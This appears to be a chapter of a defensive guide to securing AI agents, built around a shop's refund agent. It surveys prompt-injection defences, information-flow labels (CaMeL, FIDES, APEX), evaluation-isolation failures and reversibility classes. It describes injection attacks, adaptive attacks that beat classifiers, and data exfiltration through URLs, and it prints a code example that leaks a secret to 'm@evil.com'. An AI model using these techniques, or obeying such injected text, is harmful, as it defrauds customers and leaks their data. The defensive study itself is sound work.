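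OpenAI illustrates this with a coding agent assigned to fix a bug. The repository contains instructions to install an unapproved software package and switch off a security test. The agent may follow these instructions and waste some time, but the repository's rules block both changes. The agent can propose its fix, but it does not have permission to merge it into the main code.

A second model that reviews the agent's actions can notice problems that no fixed rule describes. OpenAI calls such checks advisory and says they should never be the only protection against an effect that must not happen automatically.

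### What separation of duties achieves

In accounting, the person who proposes a payment may not also approve it. Jing (2026), in *Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents*, applies this rule to agents that run commands on a computer and measures the result. (This is a different Jing from the lead author of the isolation survey.)

The design has four roles. A planner drafts an action. A policy gate, a program with fixed rules, allows the action, refuses it or refers it to a person. An executor runs only actions that have passed the gate, and an auditor reviews the log on a schedule. The agent cannot write to the gate, its rules or the log.

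The planner can submit an action as a form with fields for the operation, the file and the arguments, so the gate doesn't have to interpret a command that could be written in many ways. Each approval works only once and covers the exact bytes that will run. Otherwise, an agent could get a harmless file approved and then replace its contents.

The benchmark has 313 cases. The main result concerns 117 attacks that disguise a forbidden command, for instance by writing a file's path in an unusual form. Jing assumes the agent itself is hostile and counts every request for human approval as granted.

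| Configuration | Disguised attacks that succeed | Normal tasks denied |
|---|---|---|
| Agent runs commands directly | 98.3% | 0% |
| Gate that checks the command text | 43.6% | 0% |
| All four roles | 30.8% | 0% |
| All four roles and an operating-system sandbox | 7.7% | 11.1% |

The sandbox removes three quarters of the attacks that get past the four roles. A gate that reads commands has to recognise each way a command can be disguised, whereas the operating system checks which file the program actually opens. The benchmark does not test the sandbox alone, so the results do not show that the gate is unnecessary. The check on exact bytes addresses a different attack, in which an approved action is altered or reused. It raised the share of these attempts that were blocked from 61.3% to 90.3%.

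The sandbox denied 6 of 54 normal tasks, all because the gate allowed work in the temporary folder while the sandbox permitted writing only in the session's own directory. Matching the two lists would probably prevent most of these denials. Without that change, the same rate would send 222 of the shop's 2,000 daily cases to staff unnecessarily.

The 7.7% comes from a simulation of the sandbox, so it is less certain than it looks. Jing also ran attack commands against the real sandbox. Of the 66 that gave a clear result, 5 (7.6%) took effect. The two rates are close, but the simulation predicted none of those five. One of them deleted a file on another disk volume, where the sandbox blocked writing but not deletion. All the tests ran on a single Windows computer.

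For comparison, Jing asked three language models to judge a sample of the cases and told them to require explicit approval before any dangerous action. The models let through between 89.8% and 100% of the disguised attacks. The gap is large, though its exact size means little because the sample was smaller and had a different mix of cases.

Testing also exposed four defects that no design review had found. In an early version, approval covered only the description of an action, so swapping the file contents worked. Approvals could also be reused. A programming error made the gate refuse all actions of two kinds, which looked like strictness. The log also lost up to 31% of its records when eight processes wrote to it at once.

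Jing also cites an industry analysis warning that agents can approve their own requests by routing them through each other, which a person cannot do. A second agent is therefore a poor choice to approve the first agent's requests if the first can communicate with it.

### Whose authority applies

The gate's rules define what an agent may do, but several people may influence a single action. *Conflux* (Buckley and Schroeder de Witt, 2026) proposes that an action should go ahead only if everyone who influenced it has permission to perform it.

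In their example, Ava asks an agent to update a customer record with the status given in a report by Ben. Because the new value comes from Ben's report, the system allows the update only if both Ava and Ben may make it. If Ava asks for a calendar entry and the agent also reads a document from outside the company, the system refuses because the document's author has no right to create entries. It refuses whether or not the document contains an attack, so it doesn't need to detect injections.

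The rule depends on a record of who wrote what, because the text alone cannot show whether an action should be allowed. Buckley and Schroeder de Witt prove this with two cases in which the model receives exactly the same text, written by an authorised person in one and by an attacker in the other. A fixed rule based only on the text gives the same result in both cases, so it will either refuse a legitimate action or allow a forbidden one. Fei and colleagues prove a related limit for authorizers that read summaries.

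Under this rule, each additional author can only reduce what the agent may do, so the order of work matters. Suppose one colleague may perform only the first of two actions and another only the second. An agent that reads both their documents at the start can perform neither action. If it reads the first colleague's document and performs the first action before opening the second document, that action is allowed. A separate branch that never reads the first document can then perform the second action.

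Buckley and Schroeder de Witt prove that their rule prevents actions beyond anyone's authority, under five assumptions. Every action must pass through the check. The record must include everyone who influenced the action. The software must apply the rule as written. It must recheck permissions at the moment of execution and run exactly the action it checked. The action's list of authors must be known and not empty.

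Buckley and Schroeder de Witt acknowledge that the complete record is the hardest of these to achieve. In their counterexample, an attacker who controls a mail gateway holds back one of two conflicting messages. The agent reads only the other, a genuine message from a trusted person, and the record does not mention the attacker, even though the attacker decided what the agent would do. The proof also does not cover messages or the disclosure of data, and the researchers make no claim about how much useful work an agent could still do. Their benchmark runs so far involve only reading.

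Taken literally, the rule would stop every refund at the shop, because a customer's email influences each one and customers have no right to issue refunds. The shop would first have to decide what a customer may cause the agent to do, such as refund up to €50 on that customer's own order or change that customer's address. That decision is worth making even if the shop never tracks authorship, because the shop can then base the limits in its map on what customers are entitled to. Writing a product review, for example, doesn't entitle a stranger to trigger a refund.

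### The shop's maximum completed effect

Suppose the shop has 50,000 customer records and 30,000 orders that are still refundable, worth €60 each on average, and that on a normal day the agent issues about 100 refunds, totalling €3,000. The shop also sets limits on daily totals in its map.

| Effect | Before limits | After limits |
|---|---|---|
| Refunds | €1.8 million | €50 per case, €4,000 per day |
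| Records edited | 50,000 | 1 per case, 150 per day |
| Records deleted | 50,000 | None, only requests |
| Personal data sent to the wrong person | Data of all 50,000 customers | One customer's data, if the mail system linked the case to the wrong account |
| Misleading replies | No limit | 3 per case, 2,500 per day |

The unlimited agent would take three days to refund every order at its usual 10,000 calls a day, but the original design doesn't limit it to that rate.

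The €4,000 daily budget caps the total loss only if a person has to release the next day's budget. If the budget renews itself at midnight, an attack that nobody notices for a week costs €28,000. The daily limit also lets an attacker delay payments to honest customers by using up the budget with eighty false claims of €50.

False promises are harder to limit. The agent can still tell a customer that a €500 refund is on its way. The payment service will reject the refund, but the customer will have the promise in writing. The mail server can count replies and check their addresses, but it cannot check whether the replies are true.

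### Checking that the isolation exists

An access limit gives no protection if it exists only in the design documents. In cybersecurity tests, for example, Claude models reached real outside systems through an open connection that neither Anthropic nor its testing partner knew about. According to Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026), the connection resulted from a misunderstanding between the two companies. Anthropic discovered it when reviewing 141,006 past test runs, after OpenAI had disclosed an incident of its own. The two affected organisations that Anthropic could contact at that point had not noticed anything.

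The review missed a set of transcripts in which the agent also had internet access, including a fourth incident from January. Anthropic then searched about 481 million transcripts and found no further case of similar severity. Anthropic believes none of the four incidents would have happened if the isolation had worked as intended.

Anthropic admits in *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) that it had relied largely on one layer of defence, the configuration of the test environment. Its new rules for cybersecurity tests block internet access by default, allow a connection only to the model and keep the keys for that connection outside the environment. Testers must verify the configuration before every evaluation. They should also have the model try to break out beforehand, under close supervision and without internet access.

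Anthropic also changed how prompts describe the limits. The false statement in the old prompts may have led the model to doubt that the systems it found were real. The new prompts should include an instruction not to use the internet, which still applies if the isolation fails.

The shop can check its limits from inside the agent's environment. Using test accounts, it could try to refund €51, read another customer's order, write to an address that is not on file and open a connection to an outside website. All four attempts should fail, and the relevant service's log should show each refusal. The shop should also check that a permitted refund of €40 succeeds, because if the test account cannot issue refunds at all, the €51 refund will fail even when the payment service has no limit. Jing found a similar problem in the benchmark, where some attack commands had never reached the agent, so their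 failure did not show whether the sandbox worked.

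## Keeping untrusted content from directing the agent's actions

The limits in the shop's map cap the damage a hostile email can do, but the email can still lead the agent to do the wrong thing within those limits. Suppose the shop loosens one of them. Its payment service sends refunds only to the original card, which doesn't help customers who have closed that card, so the shop adds the option of paying into a bank account. An email then arrives from a customer's address, reporting a broken lamp and a closed card and asking for the €40 refund to go to a bank account listed in the email. The customer may well have written it, but anyone can forge a sender's address, and if someone has, the money would go to a stranger.

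Designers can try to detect malicious text before the agent follows it, or they can build the agent so that outside text does not determine its actions.

### Why filters and warnings are not a boundary

Some defences add a warning to the prompt, or repeat the user's request after the untrusted text so that the model keeps to its task. Others train the model on known attacks or put a separate classifier in front of it. Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025), in *The Attacker Moves Second*, tested 12 defences of these and similar kinds, most of which had originally reported attack success rates near zero. (Some of the 12 target jailbreaks, in which the users themselves try to get forbidden output.)

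Many of the original tests used fixed collections of known attacks. Nasr and colleagues let the attacker adapt instead. A program proposed an attack, tried it on the defended model, scored the result and used the score to write a better one. Against prompt injection defences, this search succeeded at the following rates:

| Defence | How it works | Adaptive attacks that succeed |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting, Prompt Sandwiching | Mark or repeat the trusted instructions | over 95% |
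| MetaSecAlign | Trains the model to resist injections | 96% |
| Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor | Classify text as safe or unsafe | over 90% |
| PIGuard | Classifies text as safe or unsafe | 71% |
| MELON | Runs the agent again with a harmless task and compares the tool calls | 76%, or 95% if the attacker knows the design |

The two prompt-based defences let through as little as 1% of fixed attacks, and MetaSecAlign let through 2%. More than 500 people also competed to break defences. Together they succeeded on every case in a selected subset, while the search program succeeded on 69% of those cases.

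A successful attack can look like ordinary text. The text that got past Protect AI's classifier resembled an office memo about a new company policy that required staff to log each rescheduled meeting by deleting a tracking file. A classifier strict enough to block this text would probably block many genuine memos too.

The attackers in these tests had a lot of computing power and, when attacking classifiers, saw feedback such as the confidence score. A stranger who emails the shop has neither, so a filter would probably do better against that stranger than the table suggests. Nasr and colleagues consider classifiers useful against unsophisticated attacks. But an attacker can keep sending emails. If each one independently has a 1% chance of getting through, the chance that at least one of 100 does is 63%.

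*APEX* (2026), which proposes its own defence, reports a later test of MELON with a different model, benchmark and adaptive attack. The attack success rate rose from 12.5% to 29.5% once the attacker adapted, which is still far below 95%.

### The Rule of Two as a quick test

If no filter is reliable, a designer can ask whether the agent needs to combine dangerous abilities at all. Under Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), an agent should have no more than two of these properties within one session:

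- **A:** it can process untrustworthy input.
- **B:** it can access sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** it can change state or communicate externally.

If a task needs all three, the agent should not work autonomously. A person or some other reliable check has to supervise it.

The shop's agent has all three, because it reads strangers' emails (A), looks up customer records (B) and pays refunds (C). The shop could remove A by accepting mail only from trusted senders, but it could then no longer provide customer support. Without B, the agent could not find the order. The shop could instead restrict C by having the agent draft refunds and replies for a person to release. Staff could perhaps check 100 refunds a day, but they are unlikely to manage 2,000 replies.

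Meta designed the rule for the worst consequences of prompt injection and says that it does not cover the agent's own mistakes or a user who blindly confirms a warning. The rule is also coarse, because it counts both a €5 voucher and a €4,000 transfer as a change of state. It does not show which text influenced which action.

Splitting a task between sessions can also give a false pass. Suppose one session reads the customer's email and writes a summary, and a fresh session with access to records and payments reads the summary. The second session seems to have only B and C, but it also has A because the summary may contain the attacker's instructions.

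Meta allows an agent to change its configuration during a session. For example, it may browse the web first and then lose the ability to communicate before it accesses internal systems. Any hostile text from the web stays in the context, however, so the agent should also lose the ability to change those systems.

### Separating the planner from the reader

A designer can keep all three properties in the system and divide them between two models. Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, introduced this approach. A privileged model plans and calls tools but does not read untrusted text, and a quarantined model reads the text but has no tools. Ordinary software passes data between them. If the shop wants a summary of each complaint in its records, the process could look like this:

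1. The privileged model receives the shop's instructions and asks for the email.
2. The software stores the email in a variable called *mail* and gives the privileged model only that name.
3. The privileged model requests a summary of *mail*. The quarantined model writes it, and the software stores it in a second variable, *summary*.
4. The privileged model calls the tool that adds a note to the customer's record, with *summary* as the text. The software inserts the actual words when the tool runs.

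An instruction hidden in the email can corrupt the summary, but it cannot add a step to the plan, because the privileged model never reads it.

The pattern protects the choice of action, but not the data that the action uses. If the shop's instructions send every refund to the original card, the plan takes the card from the order record, and the email cannot change where the money goes. But if the plan uses the quarantined model to extract an account number from *mail* and pays the refund into that account, a malicious email could redirect the money to a stranger even though the privileged model never reads the email.

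### CaMeL: a plan in code with a record of sources

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), adds a check on the data. As *CaMeLoT* (2026) describes it, the privileged model writes its plan as a program in a restricted form of Python. For the broken lamp, the program might be:

```
mail   = read_mail(case)
order  = get_order(case)
broken = ask_quarantined("Does the customer report damage?", mail)
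if broken:
    refund(order.price, to=order.card)
```

An interpreter runs the program and makes the tool calls. It tags every value with where it came from and who may read it. At each tool call, a policy receives the arguments with their tags and allows or denies the call. The shop could require a refund's destination to come from the order database. If a plan took the account number from the email, the interpreter would find the email among the number's sources and deny the refund.

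The privileged model has to write a program that covers every case in advance, because it cannot read the email and then add a step. This is easy when a customer reports a broken lamp, but harder when a customer has received somebody else's parcel, has already forwarded it and wants the postage refunded.

### FIDES: labels on everything the agent reads

FIDES, which Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, developed at Microsoft, lets the planner decide step by step. It attaches labels to all data. In the simplest version, data is either trusted (T) or untrusted (U), and anything derived from several pieces of data receives their combined label:

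**label(z) = label(x) ⊔ label(y)**, if z is derived from x and y

The symbol ⊔ stands for the more restrictive of the two labels, so T ⊔ U = U. For confidential data, the label lists the people who may read it, and combining two labels keeps only the readers named in both. If Ana and Ben may read one document, and Ben and Cleo may read another, only Ben may read a summary of both.

It is hard to tell which part of the context influenced a model's answer, so FIDES gives the answer the combined label of the whole context. Once the planner has read a single untrusted email, all its later decisions are untrusted.

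Each tool has limits, and FIDES allows a call only if

**label(decision) ⊑ limit(tool)** and **label(argument) ⊑ limit(argument)** for every argument,

where ⊑ means "no more restrictive than". Costa and colleagues use two basic policies. For consequential actions, the decision and any sensitive arguments must be trusted. For actions that send data, everyone who receives the data must be allowed to read it.

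FIDES keeps the planner's context trusted by hiding untrusted results in variables, as in the dual-LLM pattern. The planner may open a variable, but doing so makes its context untrusted. The planner can also ask the quarantined model for an answer in a fixed format. A yes-or-no answer carries at most one bit of information and a choice among eight categories at most three, which is too little to hold a written instruction. A policy may therefore let the agent act on such an answer.

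With this option, the shop could let a yes-or-no answer decide whether the agent refunds the original card. An attacker could still falsely claim damage, as any dishonest customer can, but could not supply an account number. The AgentDojo results below do not cover this option because Costa and colleagues left it out of the planner they evaluated.

### What the labels guarantee

The ideal guarantee is called noninterference. Let *a* ~ₙ *b* mean that *a* and *b* look the same to an observer who can see only data whose label is at most *n*. Noninterference then requires:

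**if input₁ ~ₙ input₂, then output₁ ~ₙ output₂**

For integrity, *n* is T. If two runs differ only in their untrusted data, everything labelled trusted must be the same in both. Even if an attacker rewrote the whole email, a refund that depends only on trusted data would still go to the same card.

FIDES guarantees a weaker property for secrets, called explicit secrecy. It controls where data goes, but not what an outsider can infer from the agent's decisions. For example, if the shop's agent sends reminders only to customers who owe money, receiving a reminder reveals the debt even if the text doesn't mention it. Costa and colleagues consider full noninterference too restrictive, because the agent could use almost no tools with visible effects after reading a secret.

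The danger of incomplete tracking is that leaks are easy to overlook. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, found two in CaMeL. The first occurs in programs like this one, where the balance is secret:

```
rich = True
tmp  = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the program sets *tmp* to False and CaMeL labels it secret. The program then skips the instruction *rich = False*. CaMeL raises a variable's label only in the branch that runs, so *rich* stays public, and the email goes out. If the balance is low, no email goes out. The attacker learns whether the balance is high, although no single step appears to reveal a secret. Researchers have known about this problem in conventional programs for decades.

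The second leak is in the loop that retries a failed plan. CaMeL doesn't track this loop because it runs outside the interpreter. Whether the policy blocks an attempt may depend on the secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit. An attacker who can trigger repeated attempts can recover the whole secret; for example, sixteen bits are enough to identify any whole number up to 65,535.

*Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) points out that Python's dynamic types and error handling make strong guarantees hard to establish, and recommends using a simpler, purpose-built language instead.

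Garby and colleagues developed such a language, the LLMbda calculus. Every value carries a label, and so does the conversation with the model. The interpreter stops a run if a decision based on a secret would change a conversation with a public label, because whether or not the conversation changed would reveal something about the secret. They proved a form of noninterference for every program in the language, including programs a model writes during the run, and checked the proof by computer.

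Their theorem allows for the randomness of language models by comparing output probabilities. Its one exception is that a secret may affect whether a run finishes. If two runs that differ only in the secret fail to finish with probabilities *d₁* and *d₂*, the differences between the probabilities of their visible results add up to at most *d₁* + *d₂*. If both fail to finish 2% of the time, the differences total at most four percentage points.

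### The cost in completed tasks

AgentDojo is a common benchmark for these designs. In the version that Costa and colleagues used, it has 97 user tasks and 36 attacks in four simulated environments. An unprotected agent based on GPT-4o fell for 152 injections. With label checks, no attack got through. The benchmark did count some successes, including three against FIDES, but a manual review rejected them all. The agents completed these shares of tasks when nobody attacked them:

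| Environment | No protection | Label checks only | FIDES with label checks | Tasks whose steps depend on data read |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% | 5.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% | 10.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% | 43.8% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% | 42.9% |

In the banking environment, FIDES reduced the number of completed tasks by almost half. Many of those failures were intended, because the user had asked the agent to follow instructions in a file. In the travel environment, tasks failed mostly because the model had difficulty handling variables. Using OpenAI's o1, a stronger model, raised the share of tasks completed there from 41% to 68%.

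*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) argues that such comparisons overrate the unprotected agent, because in practice a person would have to approve its consequential actions, whereas an agent with labels needs approval only when a call breaks a policy. The paper therefore counts the AgentDojo tasks that agents finished without human help. With the o3-mini model, an ordinary agent finished 24.3% of tasks this way, FIDES 50.1% and the paper's own system, Prudentia, 59.1%.

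Prudentia tells the planner what the labels and policies are, so the planner can avoid opening variables unnecessarily. It can also ask a person to endorse a piece of untrusted data, which then counts as trusted. If an email contains ten tasks, one endorsement replaces ten approvals. But the endorsement covers the whole email, so if the person overlooks an eleventh task in small print, the agent may carry that out too.

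Garby and colleagues also tested an agent written in their language on the banking tasks. With GPT-5.2, it completed 75%, compared with 37.5% for CaMeL with its policies and 66.7% for CaMeL without them. The test had only 16 different tasks, so these figures are uncertain by about 20 percentage points either way. The agent achieves its result partly by endorsing some data in its own code, which it writes before reading anything from outside. Across three models, the attacker succeeded in 2 of 1,296 attacked runs. The theorem does not rule out such cases, since endorsed data may contain an attack, but it does guarantee that endorsing data cannot expose a secret.

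### Short hints across the boundary

Some tasks are impossible if the planner learns nothing from untrusted text. For example, a coding agent cannot fix a bug without knowing what the bug report contains. *Twin Agent* (Hu, Jacob and colleagues, 2026) lets a small amount of text through. An Explore Agent reads everything but cannot take privileged actions, and a Safe Agent acts but cannot read untrusted text. The Explore Agent passes short hints to the Safe Agent. It knows what the Safe Agent has done so far, so it can limit each hint to what the Safe Agent needs next. Hints can be at most 100 or 200 characters long, depending on the benchmark, and a detector checks every one. The design relies on the observation that attacks on recent models tend to need long texts.

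| Benchmark | Agent | Tasks completed | Attacks that succeed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Software repair, GPT-5.2 | Unprotected | 61.2% | 97.0% |
| | Strict separation | 0% | 0% |
| | Twin Agent | 62.5% | 0% |
| AgentDojo, Gemini 2.5 Flash | Unprotected | 61.9% | 41.5% |
| | CaMeL | 30.9% | 0% |
| | Twin Agent | 62.9% | 0.1% |

CaMeL's 30.9% is a little low because Hu and colleagues allowed it only three attempts at a plan instead of ten. The underlying model seems to matter more, since CaMeL completed 76.3% of the AgentDojo tasks in *APEX*, which used DeepSeek-V4-Flash.

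The attacks in the table are all fixed. For a harder test on software repair, Hu and colleagues optimised malicious hints against the Safe Agent and put instructions in the bug report for the Explore Agent to copy them. The Explore Agent did so every time, but the detector stopped many of the hints. The Safe Agent carried out the malicious action in 11 of 232 cases, or 4.7%. None of these 11 attacks worked again when repeated five times each, so chance played a large part. But an attacker who can file many bug reports needs only one of them to succeed.

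When the researchers raised the limit on hints from 50 to 200 characters, the agent completed more tasks but became easier to attack. Even with short hints, it cost about twice as much to run as the unprotected agent.

A length limit would help the shop much less, because "Card closed, refund €40 to" and a German account number take up only 49 characters. In the software tests, the attacker had to get the Safe Agent to delete a file or write a secret code, which had nothing to do with the bug. But an agent needs an account number to pay a refund, so neither the Safe Agent nor the detector has much reason to flag one.

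### Unauthorised effects and unendorsed influence

*APEX* distinguishes between two kinds of attack, which explains this weakness. An attack may cause an unauthorised effect, such as a refund when the task allows none. It may also leave the planned action in place but change the information the action relies on, as when a legitimate refund goes to the attacker's account. The second kind is unendorsed influence, because the user's task did not allow that information to affect the action.

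The system, also called APEX, checks each separately. Before the agent reads anything untrusted, a model turns the user's request into a contract that lists the permitted effects and the permitted origin of each argument. At the shop, the contract might allow a refund of the price in the order record to the card in the order record. When the agent proposes a refund, APEX works out the permitted values from the contract and the results of earlier tool calls, and rejects the proposal if the amount or destination does not match.

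To detect unendorsed influence, APEX plants random tokens in places the task should not take values from. For example, it could replace the account number in the customer's email with a random token. If that token then appears as the destination of a refund, the agent must have taken it from the email, and APEX stops the payment.

No attacks succeeded on five of the six benchmarks, and 0.56% succeeded on the sixth. When not under attack, the protected agent completed 86.6% of AgentDojo tasks, and the unprotected agent completed 88.7%. Three adaptive attacks also failed completely. These are the best results of any design here, but most of the defences that Nasr and colleagues broke had also reported attack success rates near zero. Attacks by independent teams would therefore be a more convincing test.

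The contract also has to be correct. A model writes it from the user's request, and a vague request can produce one that blocks legitimate work. Some attacks satisfy even a correct contract. For example, if the user asks for a reply based on an email thread, an attacker who writes in that thread can influence the reply. *APEX* excludes such cases from its guarantee and acknowledges that a request like "execute the TODOs in this email" cannot be fully expressed in advance.

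### When the refund depends on the email

The shop meets this problem as soon as it lets customers name a new account by email. The designs would handle the €40 refund as follows:

| Design | The shop's rule is to use the original card | The shop's rule is to use the account in the email if the card is closed |
|---|---|---|
| Warning or filter | Usually pays the card, but a well-written email may change that | Pays the account unless the filter objects |
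| Rule of Two | A person releases the refund | A person has to judge whether the account is genuine |
| Dual-LLM pattern | Pays the card | Pays the account |
| CaMeL | Pays the card | Refuses, unless the policy accepts the email as a source |
| FIDES | Pays the card | Refuses, unless the policy allows an untrusted account or, in Prudentia, a person endorses it |
| Twin Agent | Probably pays the card, but a hint may change that | Pays the account if the hint passes the detector |
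| APEX | Pays the card | Pays the account, if the contract lets the email supply it |

Several designs solve the problem if the shop always uses the original card. But if the email may name the account, those designs can only block the request or carry it out. Buckley and Schroeder de Witt's proof implies that better detection would not help, because a forged email can match a genuine one word for word.

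The shop needs to know who supplied the account number. Costa and colleagues describe a more detailed label that lists everyone who could have written a piece of data. Combining two pieces of data combines their lists. The list for an unverified email includes any stranger, whatever address the email came from.

So the agent should not take the account number from the email. It could use the quarantined model to check whether the customer reports a closed card. If so, the agent sends a standard message to the address on file, asking the customer to log in and enter the new account on a form. The payment service can then accept the number because it comes from someone who has logged in as that customer. A forged email would only cause the real customer to receive an unnecessary message.

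An attacker who has taken over the customer's mailbox might still be able to reset the password and fill in the form. The shop would then lose at most €50 on the order, because the payment service still enforces its limit.

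## Sorting actions by how far they can be undone

The shop's controls now limit what the agent can do, but they will still permit some wrong actions. For example, a €40 refund for a lamp that never broke passes every check. How freely the agent should be allowed to use a tool therefore depends partly on what the shop can do after a wrong call. To label a whole list of tools, the shop needs finer classes than restorable, compensable and irreversible, and rules for assigning them.

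### The five classes

Waghmare and Sufi put every tool call into one of five classes:

| Class | Name | What recovery takes | Example at the shop |
|---|---|---|---|
| R0 | No effect | Nothing, because the call changes nothing | Reading an order |
| R1 | Restorable | The principal writes the recorded earlier state back before any outsider has seen the change | Rewriting an unsent draft |
| R2 | Compensable | A known further action leads to an acceptable state at a bounded cost | Booking a courier who charges a fixed cancellation fee |
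| R3 | Hard to recover | A person, an outside process or an unpredictable amount of effort | Paying a refund that only the customer can return |
| R4 | Irreversible | No recovery or compensation exists | Sending one customer's address to another |

R3 covers actions between compensable and irreversible. The PocketOS deletion was R3 on the Saturday after it happened, when recovering the data depended on Railway's staff. R3 also includes changes to access rights, credentials, availability and the physical world, so locking a colleague's account is R3 even if an administrator can unlock it with one click.

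Each class describes what a call does when it works as requested, and does not cover tool malfunctions. If a call has several effects, the hardest one to undo determines its class.

### When a change is restorable

R1 is the hardest label to justify, because all three conditions for exact restoration must hold. Suppose the agent edits a customer's delivery address.

- **The shop has a full record of the earlier state.** The database must have kept the old address itself. A log entry saying that the address changed at 10:02 is not enough.
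- **The shop can write that state back without anyone else's help.** If only the database provider can restore the old entry, the shop has to wait for the provider, and the edit is R3.
- **No outsider has seen, received or acted on the change.** Once the carrier has the new address, correcting the database no longer redirects the parcel.

The edit may meet all three conditions at 10:05 and fail the last one at 2 p.m., so an R1 label can expire.

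### Why the tool's name is not enough

Calls to the same tool can be harmless or harmful. Waghmare and Sufi therefore give each tool a base class that reflects its broadest effect, and add rules that assign a lower class to calls with particular arguments. A call that matches no rule keeps the base class.

These rules are easy to get wrong. For example, a database command that begins with SELECT, the SQL keyword for reading data, can still call a function that changes data. A rule should therefore describe a narrow form known to be safe, instead of checking that dangerous words are absent. The classifier applied its rules as written in all 738 checks, but Waghmare and Sufi derived the expected answers from the same rules, so the checks cannot show that the rules are right.

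An action's class also depends on the deployment. When Waghmare and Sufi closed a browser tab and reopened it with the browser's restore command, Chromium and Firefox brought back unsaved text from a plain text box, but Safari returned an empty box. The test setups differed in other ways too, so the browser may not be the only cause. Text in a richer editor was lost in all three. In a more serious example, Railway's undo window for volumes originally covered deletions in the dashboard but not through the API.

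A deployment can lower a tool's class, for example by saving a copy before each change, but it has to document the reason. It must not lower the class of a disclosure.

An unclassified tool counts as R4. This wastes someone's time on an approval if the tool is harmless, but treating unclassified tools as harmless would let the agent use a destructive one before anyone had looked at it.

MCP similarly assumes the worst about a tool that has no hints about its behavior (Model Context Protocol, 2026). A server can attach four such hints, which indicate whether the tool only reads, whether its changes are destructive, whether repeating a call is safe, and whether it deals with the outside world.

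Many tools come without hints. *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains* (Afsar, 2026) sampled 400 locally installed servers at random. The 195 that started had 2,766 tools, of which 1,626 (58.8%) had no hints. If an operator connected these servers without classifying anything, all 1,626 tools would be R4, including those that only read. Hints are also only as reliable as their source, since someone who writes a malicious server can mark a tool that deletes files as read-only.

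### When a read becomes a disclosure

Suppose the shop adds an eighth tool that fetches web pages, so the agent can check where a parcel is. The request for a page can itself carry information, even though fetching looks like R0. A hostile email could get the agent to open a link to the attacker's website with a customer's home address added to the end of the link. The attacker would then find the home address in the website's log, even if the page did not exist.

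Waghmare and Sufi's software therefore tracks the session. Once the agent has read data, any call that could carry data out becomes R4 unless every destination is on an approved list. The shop's agent starts each case by reading mail, so this rule would affect almost every page it fetches. The shop could approve the carrier's website and leave calls to every other destination at R4.

The Model Context Protocol post cites a demonstration of such a leak, in which researchers combined a malicious calendar entry, a calendar server and a tool for running code. Users often combine tools from several servers, so no server's author can know the risk of the final combination.

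### What the registry shows

Waghmare and Sufi sorted 536 tools on 20 MCP servers into their classes, with AI assistance. Sufi then reviewed a sample of 150, also with AI assistance, and left two unrated for lack of evidence.

| Class | Tools in the registry | Share | Sufi chose the same class |
|---|---|---|---|
| R0 | 333 | 62.1% | 28 of 34 |
| R1 | 31 | 5.8% | 1 of 31 |
| R2 | 18 | 3.4% | 5 of 16 |
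| R3 | 39 | 7.3% | 11 of 33 |
| R4 | 115 | 21.5% | 30 of 34 |

More than half of the 203 tools that change something are R4. Sufi's ratings matched the registry's for 75 of 148 tools, were higher for 67, and were lower for six. They disagreed most on R1, where Sufi kept only one of the registry's 31 labels. The disagreements came partly from different assumptions about who might see a change and who could reverse it. Whether a tool is R1 depends on those assumptions, so a shop should check its own systems before accepting that label.

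The match rate of 51% does not measure how accurate the registry is. Sufi is one of its two authors and approved 139 of the ratings in batches after an AI system had proposed them, so this was not an independent check. The sample also contains every R1 and R2 tool but only about a tenth of the R0 tools. Weighting the results by each class's share of the registry raises the match rate to about 74%.

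Waghmare and Sufi also tested whether MCP's own hints could replace their labels. They assigned R0 to tools marked read-only, R4 to other tools that deal with the outside world, R3 to the remaining destructive tools, and R1 to everything else. The resulting classes differed from the registry's for 118 of the 481 tools they could compare; 85 were higher and 33 were lower.

Some of this disagreement was inevitable because the hints cannot express R2, but it would affect which actions need approval. If the shop required approval from R2 upwards, 20 tools would need it under the registry's labels but not under the hints, including ten that are R4 in the registry but read-only in the hints. Another 41 would need approval only under the hints. Since the registry's labels are only drafts, these figures don't show which source is wrong.

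The registry is also a poor guide to how often agents take irreversible actions, because it counts each tool once, however often agents use it. About a fifth of its tools are R4, but only 0.8% of actual calls in Anthropic's study were judged irreversible. *An Empirical Study of Model Context Protocol Applications* (2026) cites an analysis by Stein in which tools that act directly on their environment rose from 27% to 65% of tool usage between November 2024 and February 2026. By contrast, most tools in the registry have no effect on their environment.

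The 20 servers are also not a random sample. Afsar found that 41.5% of tools lacked hints in a hand-picked set of servers, compared with 58.8% in the random draw, so the choice of servers can change such figures considerably.

### Reversibility in classical planning

Researchers in automated planning, which searches for sequences of actions that reach a goal, have a mathematical definition of reversibility. Faber, Morak and Chrpa (2021), in *Determining Action Reversibility in STRIPS Using Answer Set and Epistemic Logic Programming*, describe a state *s* as the set of facts that are true. If *a[s]* is the state after action *a*, then *a* is uniformly reversible in a set of states *S* if there is one fixed sequence of actions π such that

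**π[a[s]] = s** for every state *s* in *S* in which *a* is possible.

Suppose the agent changes a customer's address to 5 Mill Lane. If the old address could have been either 12 High Street or 3 Park Road, no fixed sequence of actions restores the correct address in both cases. But if the shop has saved the old address, *S* contains only states with that address, and writing it back reverses the change. Exact restoration therefore requires a record of the earlier state.

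The definition can misclassify an action if the list of facts is incomplete. For example, if the list leaves out what customers know, publishing a secret and then deleting it leads back to the same *s*, so publication counts as reversible. Waghmare and Sufi's condition about outsiders addresses this omission.

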